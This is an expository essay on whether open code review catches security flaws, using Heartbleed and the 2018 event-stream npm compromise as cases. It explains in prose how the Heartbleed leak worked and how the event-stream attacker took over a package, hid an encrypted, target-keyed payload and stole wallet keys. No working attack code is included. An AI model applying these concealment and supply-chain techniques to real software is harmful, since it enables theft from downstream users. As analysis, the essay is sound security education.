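# Failures of the many-eyeballs assumption, from Heartbleed to the xz utils backdoor

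## What the many-eyeballs claim says and how open-source code is reviewed

Open-source software comes with a licence that lets anyone run, study, change and pass it on. *Free-Libre / Open Source Software (FLOSS) and Software Assurance / Software Security* (Wheeler, 2006) defines the term by these freedoms, and adds that such software need not be free of charge and that companies often support it. Studying a program means reading its source code, the text that programmers write and that a computer translates into a running program. Makers of closed software usually keep their source code private.

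Many people trust open-source software because anyone can read its code, so someone should notice what is wrong with it. The best-known wording of this idea comes from *The Cathedral and the Bazaar*, an essay on the open-source operating system Linux that the programmer Eric Raymond presented at a conference in May 1997: "Given enough eyeballs, all bugs are shallow" (Raymond, 1997). A bug is any error in a program. Raymond named the idea Linus's law, after Linus Torvalds, who started Linux. It is also called the many-eyeballs claim, and it holds that flaws in code come to light quickly when enough people can read and use the code. According to eSecurity Planet's *With So Many Eyeballs, Is Open Source Security Better?* (2018), some people used the law for nearly two decades as a doctrine to explain why open-source software should be more secure. Raymond's own argument for the law was about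 debugging and did not mention security.

### What Raymond claimed

The slogan shortens a longer rule from Raymond's chapter *Release Early, Release Often*: "Given a large enough beta-tester and co-developer base ..." (Beta-testers are users who try out early versions.) The rule is more careful than the slogan because Raymond limited it to "almost every problem" and made the size of the group a condition.

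Either way, he combined three claims that can fail separately: that many people read the code, that readers find its flaws, and that the flaws they find get fixed. Publishing the code makes reading possible but guarantees none of the three. Microsoft's *Linus's Law aka Many Eyes Make All Bugs Shallow* (2006) points out that being able to inspect code does not mean anyone inspects it. The point is correct, although Microsoft sold closed software and had an obvious interest in making it.

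Raymond first wrote that every problem "will be transparent to somebody". Torvalds objected that one person usually finds a problem and another understands it, and said that finding it is "the bigger challenge". Raymond accepted the correction and held that finding and fixing both tend to happen fast.

Raymond's testers find bugs mostly by running the program. He argues that more users find more bugs because each user stresses the program in a different way, and a user who can also read the source can tell the developer roughly where the problem is. In a section added in September 2000, he described this as sampling. A program can be in an enormous number of states, and each tester tries a semi-random set of them. In his view, skill matters a lot for finding simple bugs, but for subtle ones, many people searching at once do better than a few people searching one path after another, even when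 the few are much more skilled.

That is a plausible account of how people track down crashes, but a poor one of how strangers audit code for security, which is what people usually have in mind when they cite the law today. Someone investigating a crash has a symptom to start from, whereas a security flaw often has no visible symptom because the program works as expected for ordinary users and misbehaves only when an attacker sends it unusual input.

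The same gap weakens Raymond's main evidence, the stability of the Linux kernel, because a kernel (the core of the operating system) can run for years with an undiscovered security hole. Raymond argued that if the law were false, a system as complex as the Linux kernel, with so many people working on it, should at some point have collapsed under its undiscovered bugs. Instead, it ran for months or even years without stopping.

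### How a change reaches its users

Suppose someone finds that an open-source mail program mangles long addresses, and writes a twenty-line repair. Anyone who offers a change to a project is called a contributor. Contributors are usually unpaid, and the project often knows them only by an account name. The account may belong to an honest volunteer or an AI agent (an AI model with tools that acts over many steps on its own), or it may be a sock puppet (a false identity that one actor uses to look like an independent person). The contributor submits the repair as a pull request, which is a proposed change on a site such as GitHub, or emails it as a patch. At this point, only the contributor is certain to have read the twenty lines.

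The pull request goes to a maintainer, who decides which changes enter the project and publishes its releases. The maintainer reads the repair, perhaps runs some tests, and accepts or refuses it. An accepted repair becomes a commit, a recorded change to the project's code. Other contributors can also read and comment on the change, but none has to. This review is normally the only step at which a second person reads specifically what changed. People with commit access can skip it, because they can put changes into the project without another person's approval.

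Raymond put the core of a typical project at one to three developers, with a single one common, and the "halo" of testers and possible contributors around it often in the hundreds. He considered this a strength because it limits the need for communication. If N developers must all talk to one another, there are N(N − 1)/2 lines of communication between them, which makes 45 for ten developers and 4,950 for a hundred. Members of the halo hardly need to talk to each other, since their bug reports and code changes all go through the core, so a project can add testers with little extra coordination. This is a good argument about debugging, which hundreds of people can do in parallel, but the same one to three people still have to approve every change from the halo.

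Maintainers also tire of their projects and leave, which is how Raymond's own project began. In June 1996 he sent some patches for a mail program called popclient to its owner, Carl Harris, and learned that Harris had lost interest in it. The two quickly agreed that Raymond should take over. Raymond wrote that the only question was whether he could establish that he was "a safe pair of hands". He concluded that an owner's last duty to a program is to hand it to a competent successor. Harris chose well, but the evidence Raymond describes offering was a set of useful patches, and a competent programmer with bad intentions could have offered the same.

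After enough commits, the maintainer publishes a release archive, the packaged file from which others build the program. The archive can differ from the public code history, for instance because the maintainer's tools add generated files. Someone who has read every commit may therefore not have read everything in the archive, and few people compare the archive with the history.

The program then goes to a distribution, an organisation such as Debian or Fedora that collects, builds and ships open-source programs as one system. Someone there builds the program from the archive and mainly checks that it works with the rest of the system. A person who looks after many packages cannot read each new version line by line. Some projects support reproducible builds, which let anyone build an identical program from the same source and compare it with the published one. This comparison shows when a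 published program does not match its source, but it cannot detect problems in the source itself.

Finally, the user installs the build and will most likely never look at the source code. A user who hits a bug may report it back up the path. The fix must then go through a new commit, release and build before it reaches users, so a flaw that a maintainer has fixed in public can remain on their machines for some time.

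The path also makes a small project worth attacking, because everyone downstream receives the same code. Attacking many users at once through software they all depend on is called a supply-chain attack. The twenty lines in the mail program could carry out such an attack if they contained malicious code instead of a repair.

### A simple model of detection

A little arithmetic shows what the claim needs in order to be true. Suppose that n people read a piece of code and that each of them notices a given flaw with probability p, independently of the others. One reader misses it with probability 1 − p. All n miss it with probability (1 − p)^n. So the chance that at least one reader notices is

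1 − (1 − p)^n.

The values of p below are illustrative; experiments with real reviewers have since supplied measured ones.

| Chance that one reader notices (p) | Two readers | Fifty readers | Readers needed for a 90% chance |
|---|---|---|---|
| 5% | 9.75% | 92.3% | 45 |
| 0.1% | 0.2% | 4.9% | 2,302 |
| 0.01% | 0.02% | 0.5% | 23,025 |

Raymond is right if p is 5%, because a single reader will probably miss the flaw but fifty together are very likely to find it. If p is 0.1%, fifty readers will almost certainly miss it. Time matters too, since the claim is that flaws surface quickly. If one reader would take a thousand years on average to find a flaw, fifty readers searching independently and at a steady rate would still take an average of twenty years.

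For real code, n is the number of people who read the relevant lines with some care, which can be far smaller than the number of users. Marcus Ranum, a designer of security systems, released a firewall toolkit that more than 2,000 sites used, but only ten people sent him feedback or patches. Datamation's *The Myth of Open Source Security* observes that people who do open the source tend to look at the parts they want to change, and someone adding a feature is generally not thinking about security. A program with a million users may have an n of two for any particular line, which puts it in the table's first column of results.

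The formula also assumes that readers are independent. Raymond thought that many testers do well precisely because each brings a slightly different way of looking and a different set of tools. For security there is reason to doubt this variety, because readers who lack the same training will miss the same things. Steven Bellovin, a computer scientist at Columbia University, writes in *Open Source Quality Challenge Redux* (2014) that most programmers, however brilliant, may never have been taught security. What matters to him is that people "really look" and that they use automated analysis tools as well as their eyes.

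An invented example shows how much this can lower the chance of catching a flaw. Suppose only people with certain training can see the flaw, one programmer in ten has that training, and a trained reader notices the flaw half the time. The average p is then 5%, and fifty readers drawn at random from all programmers will catch the flaw 92.3% of the time, as before. Now suppose people in a project learn from each other, so there is a one-in-ten chance that all fifty have the training and otherwise none do. The average p is still 5%, but the chance that anyone notices the flaw drops to about 10%. Adding fifty more readers who share the group's training, or lack of it, would barely raise that chance.

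So far, the security flaw has been accidental. Someone who plants a flaw on purpose can lower p by making it look like an innocent mistake, spreading the harmful part over several harmless-looking changes, or putting it in a file that nobody opens. If the flaw is a backdoor, which gives its author secret access to systems running the code, the author can make it respond only to a key that no one else holds. Raymond's testers could then sample the program's states for years without seeing a symptom. As p approaches zero, so does the whole expression, for any number of readers that a project could hope to have.

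Raymond did not allow for a malicious contributor. He wrote that contributors select themselves by being interested enough to use the software, learn how it works and produce a reasonable-looking fix, and that anyone who passes all these filters very likely has something useful to offer. A patient attacker can also pass them. *Open Source Software (OSS/FLOSS) and Security* (Wheeler, 2010) treats malicious vulnerabilities separately from unintentional ones.

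### Glass's objection and the case for open code

Robert Glass, a software engineer, criticized the slogan well before most of its famous failures. His book *Facts and Fallacies of Software Engineering* (2003) lists it as a fallacy because no study had shown it to be true, and because existing research indicated that the number of useful reviewers is small, between two and four, with each additional reviewer finding bugs at a much lower rate.

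Glass saw value in review, and one of his facts is that rigorous inspections can remove up to 90 percent of errors before anyone runs the first test. He held only that the evidence for the slogan was missing. Petersen stresses in a review of the book that Glass did not claim open-source software is worse than closed.

The formula does not obviously support his point about two to four reviewers. With p at 5%, the first independent reader adds 5 percentage points to the chance of detection and the fifth still adds about 4.1, which would not explain a sharp drop after the fourth reviewer. Perhaps the reviewers were good, with p nearer 50%, and four of them had left little to find. Or perhaps they overlapped and kept finding the same bugs. The first explanation would barely weaken Raymond's claim. The second is the blind-spot problem again, and would mean that a crowd finds few more bugs than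 a small group does.

There is still a strong case for open code. Jeff Atwood makes the central argument in Coding Horror's *Given Enough Money, All Bugs Are Shallow*, which says that code visible only to a company's ten programmers is unlikely to get as much review as code the whole world can read. In the model's terms, closed source has zero outside readers. An outsider who suspects a problem in an open program can check the code without asking the vendor. The *Secure Programming for Linux and Unix HOWTO* quotes the security specialist Bruce Schneier as saying that engineers should demand open source for anything related to security, but it notes that he attached preconditions and that attackers can read the code as easily as defenders.

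Raymond's claim about ordinary bugs has some support too. In *Open wide*, Thomas (2003) reported on researchers' mathematical model in which frequent early releases were the quickest way to bug-free code. In 2020 Idan Amit and Dror Feitelson compared popular and less popular projects from the same organisations, and found that bug fixes made up a larger share of commits in the popular ones. At Google the share was 27% higher. Google is unlikely to write worse code for its most popular projects, so the likelier explanation is that more attention uncovers more bugs. However, these are bugs of every sort, and nearly all are presumably accidental.

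Microsoft responded to the comparison with closed code by arguing that a firm can employ qualified people and assign them to inspect everything. Whether a given firm does so is as uncertain as whether volunteers do, and outsiders cannot check. A firm does have the advantage of knowing whom it has hired, while most open-source projects let strangers propose changes to the code as well as read it. The many-eyeballs claim is an argument for letting strangers read the code, not for letting them propose changes.

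## Heartbleed: a missing length check that went unnoticed for two years

OpenSSL is an open-source library that other programs use to encrypt data. It implements Transport Layer Security (TLS), the protocol that encrypts traffic between a browser and a website whose address begins with "https". In 2014 the popular web server programs Apache and Nginx both relied on OpenSSL for TLS, as did many mail servers and private networks. On 7 April 2014 the OpenSSL project disclosed a flaw, soon known as Heartbleed, that let anyone on the internet read parts of a vulnerable server's memory. The flaw had been in released versions for just over two years, and anyone could have read the faulty code during that time.

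Those lines dealt with heartbeats, short messages that let one computer check that another is still there. Seggelmann, Tuexen and Williams (2012) defined them in *Transport Layer Security (TLS) and Datagram Transport Layer Security (DTLS) Heartbeat Extension*, an internet standard also known as RFC 6520. One side sends a request containing arbitrary data, and the other sends the same data back. Heartbeats are mainly useful for DTLS, a variant of TLS for connections that do not guarantee delivery, where the only other check was a renegotiation, which takes much more work. Ordinary websites run over connections that have their own ways of checking, so they did not need heartbeats, as Durumeric, Kasten and colleagues point out in *The Matter of Heartbleed* (2014). OpenSSL switched them on by default anyway, and an operator who wanted them off had to recompile the library.

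### The bug in one message

A heartbeat request starts with one byte for its type and two bytes that give the length of the data. The data comes next, followed by at least 16 bytes of random padding. The two length bytes can hold any number up to 65,535.

Suppose a client sends the word "ping" and truthfully gives its length as 4. The whole message is 1 + 2 + 4 + 16 = 23 bytes long, and the server returns "ping" with fresh padding. Now suppose the client sends the same 23 bytes but writes 64,000 in the length field. In the flawed versions, the following happened:

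1. OpenSSL read the length field and got 64,000.
2. It reserved enough memory for a reply with 64,000 bytes of data.
3. It copied 64,000 bytes into the reply, starting at the "p" of "ping".
4. It sent the reply to the client.

The first 4 of those bytes were the client's own and the next 16 were its padding. The other 63,980 were whatever the server's memory held after the message. Miller, Kupsch and colleagues (2016) trace these steps through the source code in *Dealing with Code That Is Opaque to Static Analysis*. A single instruction copies as many bytes as the client's message specifies. OpenSSL had also stored the true length of the incoming message, but the code never compared the two numbers.

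A busy server's memory can contain other users' passwords, recent traffic and the server's private key, the secret that proves the site's identity. An attacker with that key can impersonate the site and, under the right conditions, decrypt traffic recorded earlier, although The Register (2014) stressed that the key was difficult to extract. The attacker could not choose which memory the server returned, but could keep sending requests. The bug also let a malicious server read the memory of a client that used OpenSSL.

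### What the standard required, and the fix

Section 4 of the standard already required the receiver to silently discard a heartbeat message if its stated data length was too large. It also limited a whole heartbeat message to 16,384 bytes, so a stated length of 64,000 bytes broke both rules.

Seggelmann and his co-authors published the standard in February 2012, after the code had entered OpenSSL but before its release in March. Anyone who compared the released code with the standard could have noticed the omission. Seggelmann and his co-authors thank nine people for their comments on the standard, including Adam Langley of Google, who helped write the repair two years later. People seem to have read the description of heartbeats more carefully than the code that implemented them.

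Langley and Bodo Moeller prepared the fix, and Henson, in *Add heartbeat extension bounds check*, recorded it in the project's history. Its core is one comparison:

```
if (1 + 2 + payload + 16 > s->s3->rrec.length)
    return 0;
```

The left side of the comparison is the length the message would have if its length field were correct, and the right side is its actual length. For the message with the false length field, 64,019 is greater than 23, so the function stops and sends nothing. For the message with the correct one, both sides are 23, so the reply goes out as usual. The fix also discards messages too short to be valid and repeats both checks in the separate DTLS code.

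### How two people missed the bug and two teams found it

| Date | Event |
|---|---|
| 31 December 2011 | Robin Seggelmann's heartbeat code enters OpenSSL |
| 14 March 2012 | OpenSSL releases the code in version 1.0.1 |
| 21 March 2014 | Neel Mehta of Google finds the bug, and Google patches its own servers |
| 1 April 2014 | Google tells the OpenSSL team |
| 2 April 2014 | Codenomicon, a Finnish security firm, finds the bug independently |
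| 7 April 2014 | OpenSSL learns of the second find, publishes the fix and discloses the bug |

Seggelmann was a graduate student in Germany when he wrote the code. He later told an Australian newspaper that he had "missed validating a variable containing a length" (Kobie, 2014, *Heartbleed coder*). The reviewer also missed the error. TechCentral identifies him as Stephen Henson, one of four core developers, who released the new version. According to Linux Today's *Heartbleed coder admits oversight but backs open source*, Seggelmann submitted the code at 11:59 pm on New Year's Eve but said the hour had nothing to do with the mistake.

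So at least two highly qualified people had read these lines before the release. One was the standard's lead author, and the other knew OpenSSL from working on it. Durumeric and colleagues write that a code review would probably have uncovered the bug. A code review did take place, so they presumably meant a more thorough one aimed at security. In the detection model from the previous section, two independent readers who each have an even chance of noticing a flaw will both miss it one time in four.

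In *How to Prevent the next Heartbleed*, Wheeler (2014) reports that Mehta's team eventually discovered the bug during a security review of the source code. Codenomicon's engineers found it with a new extension to their fuzz-testing tool, which sends a program large numbers of malformed inputs and monitors its behavior.

The two discoveries came twelve days apart, after more than two years without a report. Mehta's came 811 days after the code entered OpenSSL. At a steady rate of about one discovery per 811 days, the chance of a second within the next twelve days would have been roughly 1.5%. This estimate is crude because it rests on one observation, and the timing could be a coincidence. Still, it suggests that the search had not been steady and that skilled people began looking much harder at this kind of code in early 2014. Synopsys' *Diary of a Heartbleed* (2017) quotes Mark Cox of OpenSSL,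 who concluded that two finds at the same time made it riskier to leave the bug unpatched.

A malicious reader could also have found the bug first and kept quiet. Durumeric and colleagues searched stored network traffic from three research institutions and a decoy server, and found no attacks before the disclosure. Their records covered only parts of 2012 and 2013 and the months just before April 2014, so this is good evidence against widespread scanning in those periods but does not rule out a few targeted attacks.

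### Why tests and analysis tools missed it

Static analysis tools, which examine source code without running it, also missed Heartbleed. They often look for this type of error, in which code reads past the end of a piece of data. James Kupsch and Barton Miller, computer scientists at the University of Wisconsin, examined why the tools had failed. According to their 2014 analysis, which Wheeler quotes, they knew of no such tool that could have found Heartbleed when it was announced. In the later slides, Miller and colleagues add that they ran several tools on the vulnerable code, and every one missed the bug.

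To report Heartbleed, a tool has to identify the length field as untrusted input, trace its value through the program to the copy instruction, and determine that a second number, stored elsewhere, should have limited it. OpenSSL's code made this very hard. It referred to the same memory by several names and through many layers of indirection, so a tool could easily fail to trace a value to its source. Toolmakers also take shortcuts to keep analysis fast, and suppress uncertain warnings because users dislike false alarms.

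The toolmakers' own attempts support this account. GrammaTech's *Finding Heartbleed with CodeSonar* recounts that an engineer ran the company's analyser on the code as soon as he heard of the bug, and it found nothing. GrammaTech had a method for tracing data from the network, but had left it off because it was too slow. The tool found the bug when this method was switched on for the right part of the code. Wheeler rightly refuses to count this as a success, since someone who already knows where the problem is does not need a tool to find it.

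The makers of another tool, Coverity, instead changed it to treat byte swapping as a sign that a number came from outside the program. Numbers that arrive from a network usually have their bytes in the opposite order from the one common processors use, so a program has to swap them. Wheeler knows of one exception to the general failure, an open-source tool named CQual++. The evidence is an anonymous report sent to one of its developers after the disclosure, by someone who also described the tool as hard to run and interpret.

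A warning would probably not have helped anyway, because OpenSSL's developers seem to have made little use of Coverity's scanner at the time. The scanner reported 151 other defects in OpenSSL, some of which Regehr went through with a programming class after the disclosure. In *The Impact of a Major Security Event on an Open Source Project*, Walden (2020) searched OpenSSL's commit messages for mentions of Coverity and found none between 2 January 2009 and 5 May 2014, a month after Heartbleed was disclosed. That gap covers the whole period in which the bug went unnoticed, though the developers may have read some reports without mentioning them.

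Tests that run the program had a better chance of catching the bug, because one malformed message is enough to trigger it. But most developers write tests to confirm that correct input gives correct output, and every correct heartbeat worked. Measuring how much of the code the tests ran would not have helped either, because that measurement only covers existing lines and the bug was a missing check. In a discussion with Wheeler, Eric Raymond argued that a large automated test suite can bring a program close to never breaking. Wheeler agreed about ordinary defects, but he considers tests of correct input practically useless for security.

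### How far the bug reached and how fast users fixed it

Durumeric and colleagues estimated that between 24% and 55% of the https sites among the million most popular websites were initially vulnerable. The range is wide because many operators patched before anyone could measure. The upper figure is the share of these sites that supported heartbeats two days after disclosure (60%), multiplied by the share of those that ran server programs known to be affected (91%). The lower figure is the share of sites that ran such a program and supported two newer versions of TLS, which OpenSSL had introduced in the same release as heartbeats. At least 44 of the 100 most popular sites were vulnerable.

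Only Android version 4.1.1 was vulnerable to Heartbleed, according to Durumeric and colleagues. Walden suggests that the bug affected even more client devices than servers, and cites the billion Android devices that manufacturers shipped in 2014, but that figure is far too high as a count of affected phones.

All but five of the top 100 sites were safe within 22 hours, and all of them within 48. The first attack in the team's traffic records came about 21 and a half hours after the disclosure, so slower sites were at risk before they were fixed. Among the top million sites, about 11% of those using https were still vulnerable after two days and about 3% after two months. The researchers recorded 5,948 attempts to exploit the bug by the end of April, though about two-thirds came from two popular services that scanned for Heartbleed. Wheeler mentions a breach at an American hospital company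 that began with Heartbleed and exposed data on an estimated 4.5 million patients.

Installing the fix stopped further leaks but could not undo earlier ones. A site whose private key might have leaked also had to get a new key and a new certificate (the file that confirms that the key belongs to the site), and cancel the old certificate. Durumeric and colleagues followed the sites that were still vulnerable on 9 April. Within a month 73% had patched, but only 10% had replaced their certificates, and 14% of those had kept the same private key, which made the replacement pointless. Fewer than one in eleven had therefore replaced both certificate and key. This sample excluded the quickest sites, which had already patched, but a broader count in *Analysis of SSL Certificate Reissues and Revocations in the Wake of Heartbleed* (2014) also found a poor response. Three weeks after disclosure, owners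 had yet to replace over 73% of vulnerable certificates and had yet to cancel over 87%.

Durumeric's team also tested whether notifying server operators led them to patch. Three weeks after disclosure, they looked up contacts for the servers that were still vulnerable, randomly divided the contacts into two groups, and emailed one group first. Eight days later, 39.5% of the contacts in that group had begun patching, compared with 26.8% in the group not yet emailed. The emails made a large difference even though Heartbleed had been in the news worldwide for weeks.

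### OpenSSL's money and staff before and after

The OpenSSL Software Foundation, which handled the project's finances, received about $2,000 a year in donations. It also earned money from support contracts and consulting, as ADTmag's *Learning from Heartbleed* (2014) explains, though never more than $1 million in a year. The donation figure is therefore not the whole budget, although people often quote it that way. Wheeler adds that the developers sometimes turned down paid work, so the project was short of time as well as money. Consulting customers also usually want something specific for themselves, so a general audit of old code, which would benefit everyone, had no obvious buyer.

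Walden writes that the project had no full-time developers, but Steve Marquess, the foundation's president, told KALW (2014) that one person worked solely on the software and that "everyone else has outside obligations". Either way, a handful of people maintained code on which a large share of the world's websites depended, and nearly 1,500 issues were unresolved. Kerner reported in *More $ Less Heartbleed* that donors sent about $9,000 after the news broke. Marquess said this was nowhere near enough, even if the donations kept coming.

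Companies then gave larger sums. Within weeks the Linux Foundation, a non-profit, started the Core Infrastructure Initiative to fund open-source projects that the internet depends on, with backing from Google, Microsoft, Amazon and other firms. The initiative paid for two full-time OpenSSL developers and an audit, and donations paid for two more developers. By December 2014 the team had grown from two main developers to fifteen members. In June of that year the project had listed a lack of code review among its problems, and from July it required a core member to review and approve every submission. A 2017 policy raised the requirement to two reviewers.

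Walden measured what changed. The number of commits per month rose from about 46 to about 169, and the number of different people whose code went in each month rose from about 7 to about 21. The developers deleted old code and simplified much of the rest. Most telling are the security flaws that people reported (severity is on a scale from 0 to 10):

| Period | Flaws reported | Flaws per year | Average severity |
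|---|---|---|---|
| About 16 years before Heartbleed | 64 | 4.0 | 5.63 |
| 2014–2016 | 91 | 30.3 | 5.25 |
| 2017–2019 | 22 | 7.3 | 4.18 |

Only 5 of the 91 flaws from 2014 to 2016 were in code written after Heartbleed. The other 86 were in older code, and on average they were nearly as severe as the earlier flaws. Walden concludes that a low number of known flaws may only mean that nobody is putting much effort into finding them, though OpenSSL's modest count would have looked reassuring before Heartbleed.

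The study covers a single project, its data end in 2019, and only one OpenSSL developer agreed to an interview. It also cannot separate the effects of money, publicity and better tools, which all arrived at about the same time. Only sixteen of the flaw reports include the method of discovery, and all sixteen list fuzz testing. Some of the improvement therefore came from automated testing rather than from more people reading the code. AI systems have since found further flaws in OpenSSL.

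### Did the claim fail, or did it hold slowly?

After the disclosure, Seggelmann told The Guardian that the bug's eventual discovery showed the value of making source code public, as Linux Today reported. He had a point, because Mehta did not belong to the OpenSSL project and needed nobody's permission to read its code. Google could repair its own servers on the day he found the bug, and two of its engineers wrote the fix that everyone else then installed. If the library had been closed source, Google would probably have had to wait for the vendor to fix it.

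Codenomicon's discovery supports Raymond much less. A fuzz tester only needs to send messages and look at the replies. Openwall (2015) describes one such tool that works without a copy of the compiled program. Codenomicon could probably have found the same bug in a closed library, so only one of the two discoveries clearly depended on open source. Both finders were also professionals at companies with security teams, quite different from the crowd of users and co-developers Raymond described.

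The timing is also a problem for the many-eyeballs claim, which says that flaws come to light quickly. Two years is a long time for a simple bug to go unnoticed in one of the most widely used security libraries in the world. If "quickly" were dropped from the claim, every discovery would count in its favour, however late, and flaws that nobody has found could never count against it.

The opposite view, that nobody looked, fits the evidence better, although a qualified reviewer did look and missed the bug. OpenSSL had too few skilled people with the time to read old code for security, and the strongest evidence of that is the 86 older flaws that surfaced by the end of 2016. Openness did nothing to bring such people in sooner, but it allowed them to help once they arrived, and the project published a fix six days after Google first reported the bug to it.

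Heartbleed was also a fairly easy test of the many-eyeballs assumption. The missing check was a well-known kind of mistake, the standard specified what the code should do, and Seggelmann submitted his work under his own name. Some people suspected at the time that a security service had planted the bug. Seggelmann denied it, and Kobie reported the bug as an honest mistake, which is much more likely. Nobody could have settled the question from the code alone, because a check left out on purpose looks the same as one left out by accident.

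## event-stream: a package handed to a stranger in 2018

The next flaw was deliberate. In 2018 someone used event-stream, an open-source JavaScript package, to try to steal Bitcoin. JavaScript is the main programming language of websites, but event-stream was written for Node.js, which runs JavaScript outside a browser. Programs use the package to handle data piece by piece as it arrives. The attacker got control of it by emailing its author, Dominic Tarr, and offering to maintain it. Tarr had stopped using the package years earlier and handed it over.

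### How one package ends up inside thousands of others

npm is a registry from which programmers install JavaScript packages. The company that ran it has the same name. Anyone can publish there, as LWN's *event-stream, npm, and trust* explains, whereas a distribution chooses what it includes. Most packages need other packages, their dependencies, which have dependencies of their own. npm fetches all of them automatically.

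The number of dependencies grows quickly because JavaScript has no large standard library, the set of ready-made functions that comes with many languages. Programmers install small packages instead. The software consultant Hillel Wayne's analysis of the attack, *STAMPing on event-stream*, gives the example of a well-known JavaScript package for translating programs into other languages, which had 224 dependencies, while its Python counterpart had none.

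Tarr wrote event-stream in 2011. Days after the attack became public, he said in Changelog's interview *The insider perspective on the event-stream compromise* that he had twice replaced it with better designs. It became popular only after he had moved on, when a tool called Gulp used it in its documentation. By 2018 programmers were downloading it 1.5 to 2 million times a week. Snyk's *A post-mortem of the malicious event-stream backdoor* (2018) counts 3,931 packages that used it, while *A Systematic Analysis of the Event-Stream Incident* (Arvanitis, Ntousakis and colleagues, 2022) gives more than 1,500. The larger number may include packages that used it indirectly, since Wayne describes a similar total that way.

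One indirect user was Copay, a Bitcoin wallet made by BitPay. Copay used npm-run-all, which used ps-tree, which used event-stream. Wayne estimates that Copay had about 2,700 dependencies, managed by very roughly 1,700 people. Suppose each of them independently had a one-in-a-thousand chance per year of letting an attacker in, a figure invented for illustration. By the formula used for detection in the first section, the chance that at least one did so in a year would be 1 − 0.999^1,700, or about 82%. A very small risk per maintainer can therefore add up to a large one for Copay.

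### The handover and the new dependency

Tarr had 422 packages on npm and did little to maintain event-stream. Around the start of September 2018, a user named right9ctrl emailed him to say that the package had been useful and that he could spend a few hours a week on it. According to Tarr, nobody had offered to help before. Tarr gave right9ctrl commit access and the right to publish on npm. He also tried to transfer the project's GitHub page, but GitHub blocked the transfer because right9ctrl already had a copy there, so the project stayed under Tarr's name.

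| Date in 2018 | Event |
|---|---|
| 5 August | An account named Antonio Macias publishes flatmap-stream, a harmless package |
| 4–5 September | right9ctrl makes small improvements to event-stream and releases version 3.3.5 |
| 9 September | right9ctrl adds flatmap-stream as a dependency and releases 3.3.6 |
| 16 September | right9ctrl removes the dependency and releases 4.0.0 |
| 5 October | Version 0.1.1 of flatmap-stream appears, with harmful code |
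| 29 October | A user of another package reports an odd warning |
| 20 November | Ayrton Sparling raises the alarm on event-stream's GitHub page |
| 26 November | npm removes the harmful packages |

Most of these dates come from Snyk, a security company. npm's *Details about the event-stream incident* (2018) also dates the new dependency to 9 September. npm's director of security, Adam Baldwin, confirmed that date and 5 October in The Register's *Check your repos... Crypto-coin-stealing code sneaks into fairly popular NPM lib* (2018). The harmful code was available for 46 days before Sparling raised the alarm and 52 days before it was removed. Snyk's *Malicious code found in npm package event stream*, written on the day of the removal, gives 2.5 months, but that count starts in September, when flatmap-stream was still harmless.

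The attack relied on how npm handles versions. By convention, a change to the last part of a version number means a small fix, and a change to the first part means existing programs may break. ps-tree accepted any version of event-stream beginning with 3.3, so an update brought in 3.3.6 but not 4.0.0. Version 3.3.6 accepted small updates to flatmap-stream, so when the malicious flatmap-stream 0.1.1 was published, new installations picked it up without any change to event-stream.

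After 16 September, the newest version of event-stream contained no mention of flatmap-stream. Even a perfect review of the 9 September commit could not have found the harmful code, because nobody had published it yet. In the detection model, p was zero for every reader of that commit. At most, as LWN points out, a reader could have noticed that flatmap-stream had a single contributor and no previous downloads.

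The Register said that right9ctrl, the new maintainer, might not have known flatmap-stream would become malicious. That seems unlikely, given that right9ctrl chose a package nobody used and then removed it only from the version that Copay would not install. npm's report treats right9ctrl as the attacker.

### What the code did and where it was

The commit that added flatmap-stream was in event-stream's public history, but Arvanitis and colleagues found that the harmful code was only in the copy of flatmap-stream that npm distributed. The attack exploited this difference between the published package and its public code history. Some early accounts differ. The Register wrote that GitHub hosted the harmful code, and Wayne first said that part of it was there but later corrected himself. Socket's *event-stream* page reports a later attack on Axios, another JavaScript package, that also used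 a new dependency missing from the project's GitHub releases.

Part of the harmful code was in a minified file, one that a tool had shortened by removing spaces and replacing long names with single letters. Minified files load faster but are very hard to read. This code opened a second file, disguised as test data, and tried to decrypt part of it. The key was the short description of whatever project was running the code. Only Copay's description, "A Secure Bitcoin Wallet", worked. When decryption failed, the code suppressed the error.

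On Copay developers' computers, the decrypted code checked whether a build was for release. If so, it inserted more code into a barcode library that Copay also used. After the build, it restored the library's file and timestamps, leaving little for a developer to notice.

The inserted code then ran on the wallet owners' own devices. If an account held more than 100 Bitcoin or 1,000 Bitcoin Cash, a related currency, the code sent the owner's private keys, which anyone can use to spend the money, to a server in Kuala Lumpur. It also sent account details. According to npm, it did this only above those thresholds, but Arvanitis and colleagues, who go through the code line by line, write that it did so regardless of the balance.

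Almost nobody who installed the package could have seen anything go wrong. Raymond's sampling by many testers could not work here, because the harmful state existed only in release builds of one project, Copay. More users of event-stream would not have helped unless one of them was building Copay. Arvanitis and colleagues think it highly unlikely that tools that observe a running program would have caught the attack on their own. They also think static analysis was unlikely to catch it, because so much of the code was encrypted.

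### How a warning message exposed the attack

The attacker left one visible trace, a warning printed by the latest version of Node.js. The code had to try its key on every project to find out whether it was in Copay, and it did so with createDecipher, an outdated Node.js function that triggered the warning.

Jayden Seric saw the warning while using nodemon, which restarts a program when its code changes and depended on event-stream. On 29 October he reported it to nodemon's maintainers under the title *Deprecation warning at start*. A trace in the discussion pointed to flatmap-stream's minified file. Three weeks later Sparling, a computer science student in California, found code in that file that was missing from the readable source. Another user, maths22, then tried the descriptions of npm packages as keys until Copay's worked.

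Once a symptom appeared, people solved the problem much as Raymond had described. One person noticed it and others worked out what it meant. Baldwin credited the community for the find and told The Register that "there are lots of eyes on projects". But the symptom appeared only by luck, because Node.js already had a newer function for the same job that would not have triggered a warning. Snyk believes the attack would probably have stayed hidden for a long time without one.

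npm took another six days to act. Its report gives the morning of 26 November as the time its security team learned of the package, but Wayne writes that people had contacted npm's support by 22 November at the latest. He attributes part of the delay to the Thanksgiving holiday. He also found npm's instructions for reporting such problems contradictory, and learned afterwards that a bug had blocked its reporting form.

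Tarr could not remove the package either. A few weeks after the handover, he gave up about 340 of his packages, hundreds of them to an account whose password he deliberately forgot. He removed himself from packages that already had another publisher, including event-stream. He told Changelog that if he had still had access, he would have deleted the bad version as soon as someone reported it, and the affair would probably never have made the news.

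### How far the harmful code spread

Nobody knows how many people installed the malicious version. Snyk reports 8 million downloads, but that count seems to start in September. CNCF's *The event-stream vulnerability* roughly estimates over 12 million, apparently from the weekly downloads of all versions, including harmless ones. Neither figure is a count of people, because downloads include repeated and automatic installations. The spread was wide enough that Microsoft blocked the packages in Azure DevOps, which it announced in *Blocking malicious versions of event-stream and flatmap-stream packages*.

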